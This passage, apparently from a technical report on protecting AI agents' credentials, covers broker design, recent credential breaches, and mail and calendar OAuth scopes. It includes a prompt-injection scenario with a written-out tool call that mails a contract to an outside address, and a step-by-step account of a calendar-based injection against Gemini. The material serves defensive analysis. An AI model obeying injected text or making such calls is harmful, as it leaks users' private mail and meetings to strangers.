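The FRED connector failed because FRED expects its key in the web address, but the vault's record mapped the key to the `Authorization` header. FRED returned a missing-key error. Kenney and colleagues scored this failure separately from the security probes. Nothing leaked, but the failure weakens the FRED experiment more than they acknowledge. If a connector has never authenticated, a clean result from the echo services could mean either that the vault withheld the key or that it wasn't attaching the key to anything. Only the GitHub experiment rules out the second explanation.

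The experiments also left out several attacks that someone serious about stealing a token would be likely to try:

- *Redirects.* An allowed host can answer a request by sending the client to another address. If the credential goes along, the second host receives it.
- *DNS rebinding.* An attacker changes which machine a host name points to after the broker has checked the name.
- *Token refresh.* The provider returns a new token in its reply, and code in the sandbox may be able to capture it.
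- *A compromised destination.* The credential goes to the correct host, but an attacker controls that host.

Kenney and colleagues also did not verify how the vault encrypts credentials, separates one customer from another or limits what its administrators can see. They used their own judgment to score eight threats before and after adding the vault. The score for a secret pasted into a prompt fell from 25 to 4, and for replay of a long-lived token from 20 to 8. The score for an over-privileged connector fell only from 20 to 15. They did not score a break-in at the vault itself, although they note elsewhere that hosted agent platforms concentrate credentials. They cite Hugging Face, which disclosed in June 2024 that someone had gained unauthorized access to secrets stored for the apps it hosts.

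### The breach at Composio

Composio runs a broker for other companies' agents. A developer's users connect their Gmail, GitHub or Slack accounts, Composio stores the credentials, and the agent calls those services through Composio. An attacker broke into Composio's systems in May 2026. The figures in its security bulletin on the attack (Composio, 2026) are provisional, because the investigation was still open when the bulletin was last updated on 27 May.

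The attacker tried many combinations of exploits, which Composio believes a language model generated, until one worked on an internal agent that monitored Composio's infrastructure and reported connectors that had stopped working. From there the attacker reached the automated systems that repair connectors, and registered malicious tool definitions in the sandbox where Composio runs its customers' tools. The attacker gained more privileges at each step and could eventually run any code in that sandbox. Composio doesn't explain how the attacker got from the sandbox to the stored credentials.

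Composio had in effect recreated inside its broker the arrangement that a broker is meant to prevent, in which an agent that an outsider could manipulate had a path to systems with far greater rights. OpenSSH's monitor accepts only a short list of requests, while a repair system that lets someone add new tools gives an attacker many more options. Hartman's split between deciding and delivering would have helped only if the repair system could not access either part.

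The attacker obtained 5,001 GitHub connections, 12 Gmail connections, one Google Calendar connection and 28 connections to 23 other services. Some of these were Composio's own test accounts. Composio says the total, 5,042, is about 0.3% of its active connections. Allowing for rounding, that means it held roughly 1.4 to 2.0 million.

The small percentage is only partly reassuring, because it covers what Composio had confirmed, and Composio doesn't say what kept the attacker from taking more. The attacker may have been interested only in GitHub. Composio advised customers to check their GitHub activity from a period of about eight hours on 21 May.

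A cache that the attacker had probably reached also held 5,241 API keys. These appear to be the keys that developers' software uses to identify itself to Composio, since the company revoked them itself and warned that this might interrupt its customers' services. If a developer had turned off a masking setting, someone who stole their key could use it to get connected accounts' access tokens from Composio's API, even though such a key is meant to give access only to the broker and so be less sensitive than a mail token. OpenSSH's monitor has no request that returns the real credential. Composio now redacts the tokens regardless of the setting, and it hasn't reported that the attacker used the keys this way.

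Composio found that the attacker had compromised the Gmail tokens of certain employees and used magic links to enter auxiliary systems. A magic link is a one-time web address that many services email to people so they can sign in without a password. Anyone who can read the mailbox can request such a link and open it.

The exposure of twelve Gmail connections could therefore be more serious than it sounds. A thief with read-only access to Dana's mail could sign in as her on any service that accepts access to her mailbox as proof of identity.

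### Why revocation was incomplete

Composio revoked every connection it knew the attacker had exposed. As a precaution, it then revoked whatever tokens it could across about 100 services and deleted all API keys that developers had created before the night of 22 May. It also recommended that every customer have its users revoke their credentials, but some credentials stayed valid despite these steps.

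The largest gap was in canceling API keys. Providers that use OAuth commonly let an application cancel a token, but many offer nothing similar for the static keys that users create by hand. Composio could cancel these keys at only six companies, including Cloudflare and Vercel. At other providers, the key's owner had to log in and replace it. Composio also wrote to more than 50 providers so that they could cancel exposed keys whose owners Composio could not contact.

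Some OAuth tokens could not be revoked through the normal route either. If a company's administrator has approved an application for its Google Workspace, or if someone has disabled or deleted the application's registration, Google may refuse to revoke a token that still works. An administrator then has to remove the application by hand. Composio puts the share of connections it can't revoke at under 5%, but doesn't say which total it used. If the total is all active connections, the upper limit is between 70,000 and 100,000 connections.

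Users can also easily mistake deletion for revocation. Deleting a connection in Composio removes the broker's copy of the token, but the provider may still accept a stolen copy. According to Trend Micro's *The Vercel Breach* (2026), OAuth tokens survive password changes, so a new password may not help either. Google's developer guide describes an exception for refresh tokens with Gmail scopes, which stop working when the user changes the password, but this exception doesn't cover tokens for the calendar alone.

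Composio's customers were mostly other companies, which had to warn their own users. Someone in Dana's position might have had a token at Composio without ever having heard of the company. One customer, Hatz AI, reports in *Composio Tool Deprecation* that Composio first indicated it was unaffected and then, late on 23 May, recommended that everyone replace their keys and reset all connected accounts. Hatz AI switched off its Composio integrations and revoked its users' keys "where possible". Another customer, Hyperagent, published *Composio Security Incident* (2026), which gives its own recommendations to the people who used its agents.

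Even complete revocation blocks only later calls. Eight hours is long enough to copy a mailbox, and a session that the attacker opened with a magic link stays open after the mail token is revoked.

### From Context.ai to Vercel

A month before the Composio breach, Vercel disclosed that an attacker had entered its systems through Context.ai, a company it had no contract with. Context.ai had offered consumers a workspace where AI agents could act in their other applications, and at least one Vercel employee signed up with a work account. According to Context.ai's *Security Update* (2026), the employee granted "Allow All" permissions, and Vercel's Google Workspace settings let the grant take effect.

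Trend Micro traces the theft to malware that infected a Context.ai employee's computer in about February 2026. In March the attacker entered Context.ai's cloud systems and took the OAuth tokens of its consumer users. According to Vercel (2026), the attacker then took over the Vercel employee's Google Workspace account, moved from there to the employee's Vercel account, and reached Vercel's internal systems. There the attacker read environment variables belonging to a limited subset of customers. Developers keep database passwords and API keys in such variables.

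Vercel let customers mark variables as sensitive, and the attacker appears not to have read the marked ones. But Trend Micro points out that the setting was off by default, so developers had to turn it on for each secret. One employee's broad grant thus exposed the credentials of companies that had never dealt with Context.ai. Vercel closed the incident on 16 October.

Arcade, which sells a service in the same market, stresses that the breach involved neither prompt injection nor a flaw in MCP. The attacker wanted access to a store of many people's tokens.

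Context.ai detected the intrusion in March and shut down the cloud environment, but it didn't realize the tokens had been stolen until April, after Vercel contacted it. During those weeks, the stolen tokens could still work at Google even though the system that had stored them no longer existed.

*The modern attack chain* (2026), a vendor's column in Help Net Security, oversimplifies the Vercel and Composio breaches by treating them as one attack on two targets, with a stolen OAuth token as the way in. Composio says its attacker got in through its monitoring agent, and Vercel hasn't disclosed how its attacker got from the employee's Google account to the Vercel account. But the column is right that a mailbox often gives access to much more than mail.

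### One store or many copies

Brokers are thus large targets for attackers. Without one, most developers would leave copies of credentials wherever their agents need them, and those copies also leak.

*Caging the Agents* (2026) reports on the security of a company's fleet of AI agents in healthcare. Before the company introduced a broker, an audit found credentials in shell startup files, in configuration files that any user of the machine could read, and in settings files inside the agents' workspaces. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) found 1,708 security issues in 520 skills, which are third-party packages of instructions and code that people add to agents. Debug logging accounted for 73.5% of the vulnerabilities, because agent frameworks feed a program's printed output into the model's context. A developer who prints a token while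 debugging therefore exposes it to the planner.

Attackers can also find leaked credentials faster than before. Help Net Security's *ARTEX goes from pentesting tool to attacker staple in three months* (2026) reports Microsoft's findings on ARTEX, a tool whose AI agents carry out intrusions. Since August, attackers have used it to search GitHub for leaked secrets and break into cloud accounts with the ones that still work. In one case, an agent went from searching GitHub to stealing data in five minutes. The agents also stole secrets from Microsoft's vault service, so a leaked credential can expose even secrets kept in a vault.

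A rough way to compare a broker with scattered credentials is to estimate how many credentials would leak in a year. If *N* scattered credentials each leak with probability *p*, an average of *Np* leak. If one broker holds all *N*, an attacker breaks in with probability *q*, and a break-in exposes a fraction *f* of them, an average of *Nqf* leak. The broker leaks fewer on average if *qf* is smaller than *p*.

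If *f* is 0.3%, Composio's figure, a broker that was broken into once every year would expose only three in a thousand credentials each year. Developers who kept their own copies would have to keep 99.7% of them safe each year to do as well. Nobody has measured *p* for agents' credentials, but the findings of the healthcare audit and of Chen and colleagues make that rate seem unlikely.

The weak point of this calculation is *f*. Composio's 0.3% comes from one attack, and nobody outside the company can explain why it didn't expose more. The next attacker might take everything. The value of *q* also depends on *N*, because a store with two million connections attracts attackers who wouldn't bother with Dana's laptop. The average also hides that scattered copies leak a few at a time, while a breach at a broker forces everyone who uses it to act at once. Every developer who used Composio had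 to replace their keys, including those whose users' connections were never exposed.

Two other breaches suggest that Composio's was not an isolated case. In August 2025, attackers stole tokens from Salesloft, whose Drift chatbot connected to customers' other software. Krebs on Security's *The Ongoing Fallout from a Breach at AI Chatbot Maker Salesloft* (2025) reports that the attackers took tokens for hundreds of online services and used some to read mail in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. Petri's *Why OAuth Blind Spots Keep Putting SaaS Supply Chains at Risk* quotes an estimate that the breach affected more than 700 companies.

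The more recent breach hit OpenCode, which makes a coding agent. Its Console service is a credential broker that stores a team's keys to AI models and attaches them to the team's requests, so individual members never hold them. *OpenCode Breach Could Affect OpenAI, Anthropic and Google* (Infosecurity Magazine, 2026) reports that in October 2026 an intruder got into a legacy system that OpenCode was about to retire, and may have exposed the keys of 1.4% of Console's users.

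For most developers, a broker still looks safer than scattered copies of credentials, mainly because the copies leak in many ordinary ways. The case for pooling thousands of customers' credentials at one company is much weaker. Dana's assistant needs a separate process to keep the token away from its planner, but that process doesn't also have to hold two million other connections.

### Encryption keys that the customer holds

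After its breach, Composio announced that it was moving toward a system in which customers keep their own encryption keys. In such systems, the broker usually encrypts the stored credentials with a data key, which it keeps only in encrypted form. The master key that decrypts the data key stays in the customer's account at a key management service. WorkOS (2025) introduced such an option for its own vault. The customer can audit every use of the master key and can cut off the vault's access by revoking it.

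This protects well against someone who copies the broker's database or finds an old backup, but much less against someone who controls the running broker. To send Dana's message, the broker has to decrypt her token, which requires access to her company's key service to unlock the data key. An attacker running code as the broker has the same access. Writer, which offers customer-held keys for its AI platform, documents that it keeps an unlocked data key in memory for five minutes at a time, during which the key can be used without another request to the key service.

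Whether such keys would have stopped Composio's attacker depends on whether the sandbox where he ran his code contained decrypted tokens. Encryption did little to protect the variables that the attacker read in the Vercel breach, because he decrypted them through Vercel's own systems. Such keys do let customers cut off access without the broker's cooperation, but customers have to know when to do so, and Context.ai took about a month to recognize the token theft.

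### Shorter lifetimes

Expiry disables a stolen token even if nobody has noticed the theft. Gainsight, a business software company, says that someone obtained a set of OAuth tokens around August 2023, and that attackers used them to enter customers' Salesforce accounts in October and November 2025. Its logs went back only one year, so its investigators could not establish where the tokens had come from. If the tokens had expired after even a few months, they would have stopped working long before anyone tried them.

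A broker can't make every credential it stores short-lived. Dana's assistant has to work while she is asleep, so the broker keeps her refresh token. A thief who steals it can get new access tokens, and their short life then offers little protection. If the application runs on a server, the thief also needs its client secret to use the refresh token, so it makes sense to store the two separately, though a thorough break-in would probably expose both.

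Forrester's *Game Over For Trust*, a commentary on the Vercel breach, recommends combining short-lived credentials with tokens bound to their sender. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) tests this combination on a small scale. Its broker, about 160 lines of Python, issues short-lived tokens that work only for the agent they name, and it checks every tool call. Stealing and replaying a token worked in the ordinary setup but failed with the broker. The broker's developers ran the test themselves, and it covered only the tokens that agents present to the broker, not the credentials the broker stores, which are the kind attackers took at Composio and Salesloft.

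Restricting the internet addresses from which a token works is cruder, but it has stopped a real attack. Okta's tokens were among those stolen from Salesloft, but Petri reports that the thieves couldn't use them because Okta allowed access to its Salesforce account only from known addresses. Composio has since restricted its customers' API keys in a similar way. The restriction fails if the attacker sends requests from the broker's own machines, because their addresses are allowed.

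### A broker for one customer

Each agent in the healthcare fleet described in *Caging the Agents* has its own sidecar, a second container that holds the agent's credentials and adds them to its requests. Composio, by contrast, keeps credentials in a shared store. The sidecar also limits how often the agent can call, which destinations it can reach and how much data it can send at a time. Breaking into one sidecar exposes only that agent's credentials, so an attacker would have to break into many sidecars to steal credentials on a large scale.

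The OpenCode breach gives this design some support. According to Clubic's *OpenCode piraté, des clés API exposées et des utilisateurs facturés*, keys that developers had kept only in OpenCode's local application were unaffected. Users of the hosted Console reported charges of up to 1,700 dollars for requests they hadn't made. But an agent may be able to read a key stored in a local application, so the developers who kept their keys there avoided this breach but weren't necessarily safer overall.

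Okta's tests show that storing a credential locally isn't enough to keep it safe. OpenClaw can store secrets in an unencrypted configuration file that the agent can open. Keychain encrypts its contents, but it is designed to return a secret to a program that has permission. In one test, the user had told macOS always to allow access to certain items, and the agent retrieved a Wi-Fi password and passed it to the attacker. A local broker therefore has to use the secret on the agent's behalf and never return it.

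A company that runs a local broker has to update the software, protect the machine and notice intrusions itself. A hosting provider with a security team will often do this better than a small firm. A sidecar also shares an operating system kernel with the agent, an arrangement Infisical warns against. If a company can maintain a broker on a separate machine that stores only that company's credentials, it avoids both the shared kernel and a store that holds many companies' credentials.

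An attacker who takes over the agent can still send requests to the broker, wherever it runs. *Caging the Agents* acknowledges that the attacker would gain access to the sidecar's interface, though not to the keys behind it. What he could do to Dana's mail depends on how much access the token gives and which calls the sidecar allows.

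## How narrowly can access to mail and calendar be granted?

The mail API allows a request only if the token's scopes cover it, whether the request comes through a broker or from someone who stole the token. The provider defines the available scopes. The developer of Dana's assistant chooses from them, and Dana agrees or refuses, but neither can add one that more closely fits what she asked the assistant to do.

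### The scopes on offer

The table lists the closest matching scope for each kind of access in Gmail, Google Calendar and Microsoft Graph, the API that software uses to reach Microsoft mailboxes and calendars. Microsoft calls scopes "permissions". The table omits the long prefix from Google's scope names.

| Access | Google | Microsoft Graph, for a signed-in user |
|---|---|---|
| Read mail | `gmail.readonly` | `Mail.Read` |
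| Read mail without the body | `gmail.metadata` | `Mail.ReadBasic` |
| Write drafts | `gmail.compose`, which also sends | `Mail.ReadWrite`, which also reads and deletes mail but can't send |
| Send mail | `gmail.send` | `Mail.Send` |
| Change settings | `gmail.settings.basic` | `MailboxSettings.ReadWrite` |
| See free and busy times | `calendar.events.freebusy` | No separate permission |
| Write events | `calendar.events.owned` for the user's own calendars, `calendar.events` for all she can use | `Calendars.ReadWrite` |

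Google sorts Gmail scopes into three tiers and requires more checks for applications that request higher ones. Sending mail is in the middle tier, while reading headers is in the top tier, where an application that stores the data on its servers must pass a security assessment. This order makes sense if the main danger is a company that collects people's mail, but it is a poor guide for an agent that strangers can manipulate, because the contract would leave Dana's mailbox in a message the agent sends.

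The assistant doesn't need to change mailbox settings, so its developer should leave out `MailboxSettings.ReadWrite`. That permission covers automatic replies, which go to people who write to Dana, and inbox rules, which can forward her incoming mail, even though Microsoft notes that it doesn't include permission to send mail. An attacker who got the planner to create a forwarding rule would keep receiving her mail even after she switched the assistant off.

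Google's free/busy scope shows when someone is busy but not the titles or descriptions of events, so an invitation can't pass instructions to the planner through it. Cronofy, a scheduling service, offers a connection to Google that requests little more than this scope and the list of the user's calendars. Microsoft's closest permission, `Calendars.ReadBasic`, leaves out an event's body and attachments but includes its title, where a stranger can still write instructions. *Microsoft OAuth scopes for email and calendar*, a guide from Nylas, which connects applications to mail providers, lists the broader `Calendars.Read` permission for free/busy lookups, though Microsoft's Graph API may accept a narrower one.

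### Drafts that the assistant can't send

Dana might prefer an assistant that drafts replies and leaves her to send them. No Gmail scope lets an ordinary application write drafts but not send them. Google describes `gmail.compose` as "Manage drafts and send emails", and its scope for add-ons, small programs that run inside Gmail, also covers both.

With Gmail, the broker therefore has to enforce the limit. Blocking the endpoint for sending a message isn't enough, because Gmail has a second endpoint for sending an existing draft. It also accepts batch requests, which pack several calls into the body of one request and can include a send call. The broker should keep a list of the paths and methods the agent may use and refuse all others. A broker that only mints tokens can't do this, because the agent then calls Gmail directly.

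Microsoft uses separate permissions for drafting and sending mail. An application with only `Mail.ReadWrite` can create a draft but needs `Mail.Send` to send it, so someone who steals its token can't send mail either. But `Mail.ReadWrite` covers the whole mailbox, so an assistant that Dana trusts only with drafts could also alter or delete her other mail.

### Invitations as outgoing mail

An assistant without permission to send mail can still send text if it can write calendar events, because the calendar service can email an event's description to its guests. Microsoft's server sends invitations to the attendees of a new event. Google's API lets the caller choose whether to send them, using the `sendUpdates` parameter.

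A planner influenced by the stranger could therefore create an event, add his address as a guest and paste the contract into the description. The provider would check only for calendar access. A broker could force Google's parameter to `none`, but the event might still appear in the guest's calendar. Refusing any event with guests would be safer, but Dana would then have to invite people herself.

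### The smallest set for Dana's request

Dana asked her assistant to answer this week's meeting requests and book them. With Google, a minimal set of scopes is:

- `gmail.readonly`, to find and read the requests
- `gmail.send`, to answer them
- `calendar.events.owned`, to see her own events and create new ones
- `calendar.events.freebusy`, if the assistant also has to compare her colleagues' calendars

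With Microsoft, she would need `Mail.Read`, `Mail.Send` and `Calendars.ReadWrite`.

These sets would prevent an attacker who controlled the assistant, or stole its token, from deleting her mail or creating a filter to hide replies that might alert her. With Gmail, he also couldn't delete the copy of a sent message from her Sent folder, but with Microsoft he could avoid leaving one, because a program that sends mail through Graph can ask the server not to save a copy.

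But the assistant can still read every message in the mailbox, including years-old ones. It can send any of them to anyone, any number of times, in Dana's name. It can also delete all the events in her own calendars. The stranger's attack therefore still works with the minimal set.

In *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*, Noyan proposes choosing permissions separately for each task. The user's role would set an upper limit, a classifier would estimate what the task needs, and a policy would forbid certain combinations. Forbidding an agent to combine private mail with outside recipients would prevent the theft of the contract, but it would also prevent Dana's assistant from answering clients.

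### What a scope can't describe

Dana would probably describe the limits differently. She might tell a human assistant to write only to people who had asked for a meeting, and to send each of them only one message, about the meeting, in the same thread.

No scope in the table can express any of these limits. Microsoft builds its permission names from a resource, an operation and a constraint, as in `Mail.Read.Shared`. The constraint sets how much of an organization's data the application can reach, but no part of the name specifies a recipient or a number of messages. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) attributes this to the design of scopes, which specify an operator, such as "send", but not its operands, such as the recipient and the text. The server therefore treats every action that the scope permits the same way.

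Some of Dana's limits would be easier to enforce than others. The request includes the recipient and thread, so software outside the planner could check them against a list, and it could also count messages. The purpose is harder to enforce because no field in the request records it. A reply that confirms a meeting can have the same recipient, thread and length as one that discloses a client's price.

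### MiniScope

Even choosing among the existing scopes is harder than it looks, because many API methods accept any one of several scopes. *MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) automates the choice. It also acts as a broker, checking each call against the scopes the user has granted.

MiniScope starts from each service's documentation, which lists the methods that every scope permits. If one scope's methods are a subset of another's, the system places the first below the second in a hierarchy. When the agent submits a plan, an optimizer finds the cheapest set of scopes that covers every call in it:

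```
minimize    Σ cost(v) · x(v)    over all scopes v
subject to  Σ x(v) ≥ 1          over the scopes that permit call i,
                                for every call i in the plan
```

Here *x(v)* is 1 if the set includes scope *v* and 0 if it doesn't, and *cost(v)* is the number of methods the scope permits. The optimizer includes scopes the user has already granted in the set. If the plan needs a scope the user hasn't granted, MiniScope prompts the user to allow it once, for the session or always, or to refuse it.

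In one MiniScope example, a user asks for a reply to an email about an event. The email contains an instruction to delete it afterwards, and the planner adds the deletion to its plan. MiniScope finds that the new plan needs permission to delete mail and asks the user, who refuses.

MiniScope measures a scope's size by the number of methods it permits, so it can choose a scope that exposes more calendars. Zhu and colleagues observe that Google's calendar scopes don't nest as their names suggest. `calendar.events.owned` permits more methods than `calendar.events`, even though it covers only the calendars that the user owns. When both permit the planned calls, MiniScope would choose `calendar.events`, and Dana's assistant could then edit colleagues' calendars that she has permission to change. Zhu and colleagues allow for other measures, and one that counted the calendars and messages within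 reach would suit Dana better.

There may also be no single smallest set of scopes. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that Google lists alternative scopes for a method and leaves the choice to the developer, and that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether their optimum is unique. Dana's assistant could do without `calendar.events.owned` if it used the free/busy scope to find a time and `calendar.app.created` to put the meeting in a separate calendar that it creates. It then couldn't read or delete her existing events, but it could create new calendars, which the first set doesn't allow. Neither set contains the other, so someone has to decide which risk matters more.

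Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope on requests that a language model had written for ten real applications, including Gmail, Google Calendar, Outlook and Slack. They compared it with language models that received the same plans and scope lists. Models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google chose a minimal set of scopes 70–83% of the time, and two open models did so 20–34% of the time. MiniScope's own optimizer determined which sets counted as minimal, so these figures depend on the measure it minimizes. The models did worst on services with deep hierarchies, such as Google Calendar.

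The optimizer has a clearer advantage in speed. For tasks that involved several applications, an agent with no checks took 4.91 seconds, one with MiniScope took 5.23, and one that used GPT-5 to choose the scopes took 20.50. These times exclude how long the user takes to answer confirmation requests. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, MiniScope asked for confirmation on 18–60% of requests, depending on how cautious the simulated user was. A user who always chose "Always allow" soon stopped being asked, but by then the agent had permanent access to everything it had requested.

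Zhu and colleagues also examined the connectors that ChatGPT and Claude offered in 2025, and found six that requested more access than their tools needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector requested scopes that permitted 50 methods when 32 would have been enough. ChatGPT's Gmail and Calendar connectors were described as read-only but could have modified and deleted messages and events. Claude's connectors for the same two services requested no extra access. These were widely used products from companies with large security teams, so smaller developers probably make the same mistake.

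MiniScope doesn't protect against misuse within a scope the user has granted, and Zhu and colleagues don't claim it does. Once Dana has allowed reading and sending, the stranger's paragraph triggers no new permission prompt. Zhu and colleagues suggest that the system could also check the arguments of tool calls, for example by limiting Slack messages to one channel, but they left this out of the basic design because they expect people to approve long lists of detailed permissions without reading them.

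### Finer requests and narrower tokens

Several OAuth extensions can limit access more narrowly than a fixed list of scopes. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (2026) summarizes three of them: token exchange, rich authorization requests and resource indicators.

In *token exchange* (RFC 8693), a program presents a token to the authorization server and requests a different one. Suppose Dana's assistant uses a second agent to compare calendars. The assistant could exchange its own token for one that covers only free/busy times and give that to the second agent. The new token can also record that the second agent is acting for Dana, so the calendar service can distinguish the agent's requests from Dana's. But the authorization server sets how much access the new token carries, and the standard doesn't require it to carry less than the original.

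*Rich authorization requests* (RFC 9396) replace the scope label with a structured description. For the reply to Lee, it might look like this:

```
{"type": "mail_reply",
 "actions": ["send"],
 "recipient": "lee@client.example",
 "thread": "th-4821",
 "max_messages": 1}
```

This would express most of what Dana wants, but the API's owner has to define each type and check its fields on every call. The `mail_reply` type here is only an illustration.

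*Resource indicators* (RFC 8707) tie a token to one audience, the service that should accept it. A calendar service that received such a token from Dana's assistant couldn't use it to open her files at another service.

The mail providers offer little of this for Dana's token. Google supports token exchange for its cloud platform, but that doesn't narrow a Gmail token to a single thread. Microsoft's "on-behalf-of" exchange uses a different OAuth extension and returns a token with ordinary Graph permissions. Neither company's mail scopes include structured fields for recipients or threads. Microsoft's tokens specify an audience, but for mail that audience is all of Graph, which also covers calendars and files.

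The original OAuth standard of 2012 lets an application ask for fewer scopes when it renews an access token. A broker could therefore use one refresh token to obtain an access token that only sends mail and another that only reads free/busy times. A thief who copied either access token would get less access, but could still use the sending token to email any recipient.

According to *Delegation Without Trust*, the July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) requires audience binding, meaning that each token must name the one MCP server it is for. The protocol also forbids servers from passing the client's token to another service, so an MCP server for Gmail must obtain a separate token from Google for its calls.

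The rule prevents a form of the confused deputy problem that Hardy described. If servers passed tokens along, Gmail could receive a token that Dana had meant for another service and treat the server's request as hers. Under the rule, the server holds a Google token for every user, which makes it another target for attackers. The rule also doesn't narrow the Google token, which has the same scopes as any other application's.

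Most of these controls decide whether an agent may use something that already exists, but a permitted call can return something new. For example, if the assistant books a video meeting, the reply may include a link that lets whoever opens it run the meeting. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* addresses the need to decide whether the agent may use such a resource or pass it on.

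### Passing access from agent to agent

A developer may divide Dana's task among several agents, with one to read mail, one to compare calendars and one to write replies. Each should receive less access than the agent that called it, but common agent software does little to ensure this.

*Delegation Without Trust* examined four widely used frameworks in their default configurations by running a test on LangGraph, inspecting the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and reading the specification of MCP. LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen had no built-in limits on what a second agent could do with access it received. MCP's token rules set some limits, but nothing in MCP narrowed access as one agent called another or recorded the chain of agents.

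The paper then simulates 2,000 cases in which an attacker takes over one of the lesser agents. An agent with an ordinary broad token could perform all 8,100 actions possible in the environment. With tokens that the paper's broker had narrowed for each task, it could perform 1.5 on average. The ratio means little because the size of the environment was chosen for the simulation. The useful result is that, with narrowed tokens, the number of possible actions depended only on the task and would stay the same if the company added more services.

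*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a review of 89 sources, proposes tracking where information came from as well as who gave authority to whom, from the user through the company that runs the agent to each agent and tool. Both matter for Dana's mailbox, because the assistant needs her authority to open it, and the text inside comes from people who have no authority over the assistant. A scope deals only with authority, so it doesn't track where the text came from.

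The review finds that few documented deployments can reliably trace an agent's actions to a person, keep those actions within what that person delegated, and let the person contest them afterwards. It names two main gaps, in enforcement at the time of each call and in limits on the combined effect of many calls. Dana's case illustrates the second gap. Each reply may be harmless, but the scopes don't prevent the assistant from sending a thousand replies or disclosing a confidential document one sentence at a time.

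### An account of the agent's own

So far, Dana's assistant has used her account through a token she delegated to it. The alternative is to give the assistant its own identity, which can mean two different things.

Microsoft distinguishes delegated permissions, which an application uses on behalf of a signed-in user, from application permissions, which work with no user present once an administrator has approved them. An application permission gives the agent its own identity but can greatly increase its access. As an application permission, `Mail.Read` covers every mailbox in the organization, and `Mail.Send` lets the agent send as any user. Administrators can restrict both to specific mailboxes, and should do so for an assistant that serves one person.

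Microsoft's *Least privilege for AI agents* (2026) warns that an agent without its own managed identity and narrow roles may reach data nobody meant it to have. The narrow roles are as important as the identity, because an agent with a separate account but a broad role can still read everyone's mail, even if it is easy to identify in the logs.

The other option is to give the assistant an ordinary user account with its own mailbox, like the account a company would give a human assistant. Dana forwards meeting requests to it, or asks people to write to it directly, and shares her calendar with it. The assistant's token then gives access only to its own mailbox and what she has shared. A manipulated planner can't find the confidential contract unless someone sent it there. A thief who read the assistant's mail also couldn't use magic links to sign in to other services as Dana.

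Calendar sharing can also limit access more narrowly than scopes can. Microsoft has no permission just for free/busy times, but Dana can share her Outlook calendar so that others see only when she is busy. The assistant can then find a free half hour, create the meeting in its own calendar, and invite both Dana and the client. Dana accepts the invitation as usual, so the assistant never needs to write to her calendar.

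Separate accounts also make the records clearer. When the assistant uses Dana's token, the provider's logs can show which application made the call, but the recipient sees a message from Dana. If the assistant has its own address, the recipient can tell who wrote, and an administrator can suspend the account without locking Dana out of hers. The company still has to record whom the assistant works for, because otherwise the logs will show that the assistant acted but not who asked it to.

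With a separate mailbox, though, Dana has to forward the requests that reach her own address, and some clients may dislike receiving replies from an assistant. The forwarded messages still contain whatever strangers wrote in them, and that text could manipulate the planner into revealing one client's message to another or sending invitations to people Dana has never met.

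## How can a manipulated planner do harm with calls it is allowed to make?

Suppose Dana's assistant has every protection described so far. Her token is in a broker on a separate machine, the broker adds it only to requests for her mail provider, and the token has only the scopes needed to answer meeting requests. Then the stranger's email arrives, with its paragraph asking for the contract.

### The contract leaves through a working broker

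The planner reads the whole message and follows the paragraph. It first proposes a mailbox search for the contract. The broker adds Dana's token to the request, and the mail API returns the message that contains the file. The planner then proposes this call to the send-message tool:

```
{"to": "files@outside.example",
 "subject": "Contract",
 "text": "The document is attached.",
 "attachments": ["contract.pdf"]}
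```

The broker adds the token again, the API sends the message, and the assistant goes on to confirm the meeting. The token never reached the planner or the sandbox. Three components handled the call on its way out:

| Component | What it checks | What it finds |
|---|---|---|
| Harness | Whether the tool exists and its arguments have the right form | A send-message tool and a well-formed address |
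| Broker | Which agent is calling, and the host, path and method | Dana's assistant, her mail provider and the sending endpoint |
| Mail API | Whether the token is valid and covers the operation | A valid token with permission to send |

All these findings are correct, and they would be the same for the message to Lee. The attachment isn't suspicious in itself, since Dana might have asked her assistant to send this contract to her lawyer. That call could differ from the one that emails the stranger only in the address, and refusing it would be a mistake. The right decision depends on whether Dana wanted the message sent. The best evidence of that is the sentence she typed, but the broker and the mail API never receive it, and the harness only passes it on to the planner.

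Common agent software leaves the same gap. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined the public code of LangChain with LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's toolkit for agents that handle payments. All three let developers choose which tools an agent has, but by default none checks the values in a call against a policy before running it. In a demonstration with a simulated payment system, LangChain's ordinary code ran a call that redirected a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account. The account number had the right format, and the code did not check who owned the account. Developers can add such a check, and Mellafe Zuvic offers one called ScopeGate.

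### A summary hidden in a calendar

In January 2026, the security company Miggo disclosed a way to steal meeting details through Gemini, Google's AI assistant, which can read and write its user's Google Calendar. According to The Hacker News, which received Miggo's report, the attack worked like this:

1. The attacker created a calendar event, wrote instructions for the assistant in its description, and invited the victim.
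2. The instructions had no effect until the victim asked Gemini an ordinary question, such as whether there were any meetings on Tuesday.
3. Gemini read the calendar to answer the question, including the attacker's description.
4. Following the instructions, Gemini summarized all the victim's meetings for a particular day, including private ones.
5. Gemini created a new event and put the summary in its description.
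6. Gemini gave the victim a harmless answer.

In many companies' calendar configurations, the attacker could see the new event and read the summary. This is probably because these companies let colleagues see each other's events, in which case the attacker would need an account at the company or some other access to the calendar.

Miggo says the attack needed no direct interaction from the user. The victim didn't have to do anything with the invitation, but did have to ask Gemini about their schedule. People ask calendar assistants that question all the time, so the attacker only had to wait.

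Gemini read events, summarized them and created one, all of which is normal for a calendar assistant. It was allowed to read the private meetings because its user was. The original events stayed private, but their contents were now in an event that other people could open. A calendar's privacy settings apply to each event, so a private event's settings don't cover information that an assistant copies out of it.

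The instructions also looked ordinary. SecurityWeek's *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini* quotes Miggo's explanation that the text was plausible as a user request and became harmful only when the model carried it out with its tools. A filter for suspicious wording would find little to flag, since a user might type "summarize my meetings and put the summary in a new event." Google confirmed the flaw and fixed it.

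This theft required no permission to send mail. The data reached the attacker without leaving Google's calendar service, so a company monitoring its outgoing mail and web traffic would not have seen it.

### A web address that carried the data

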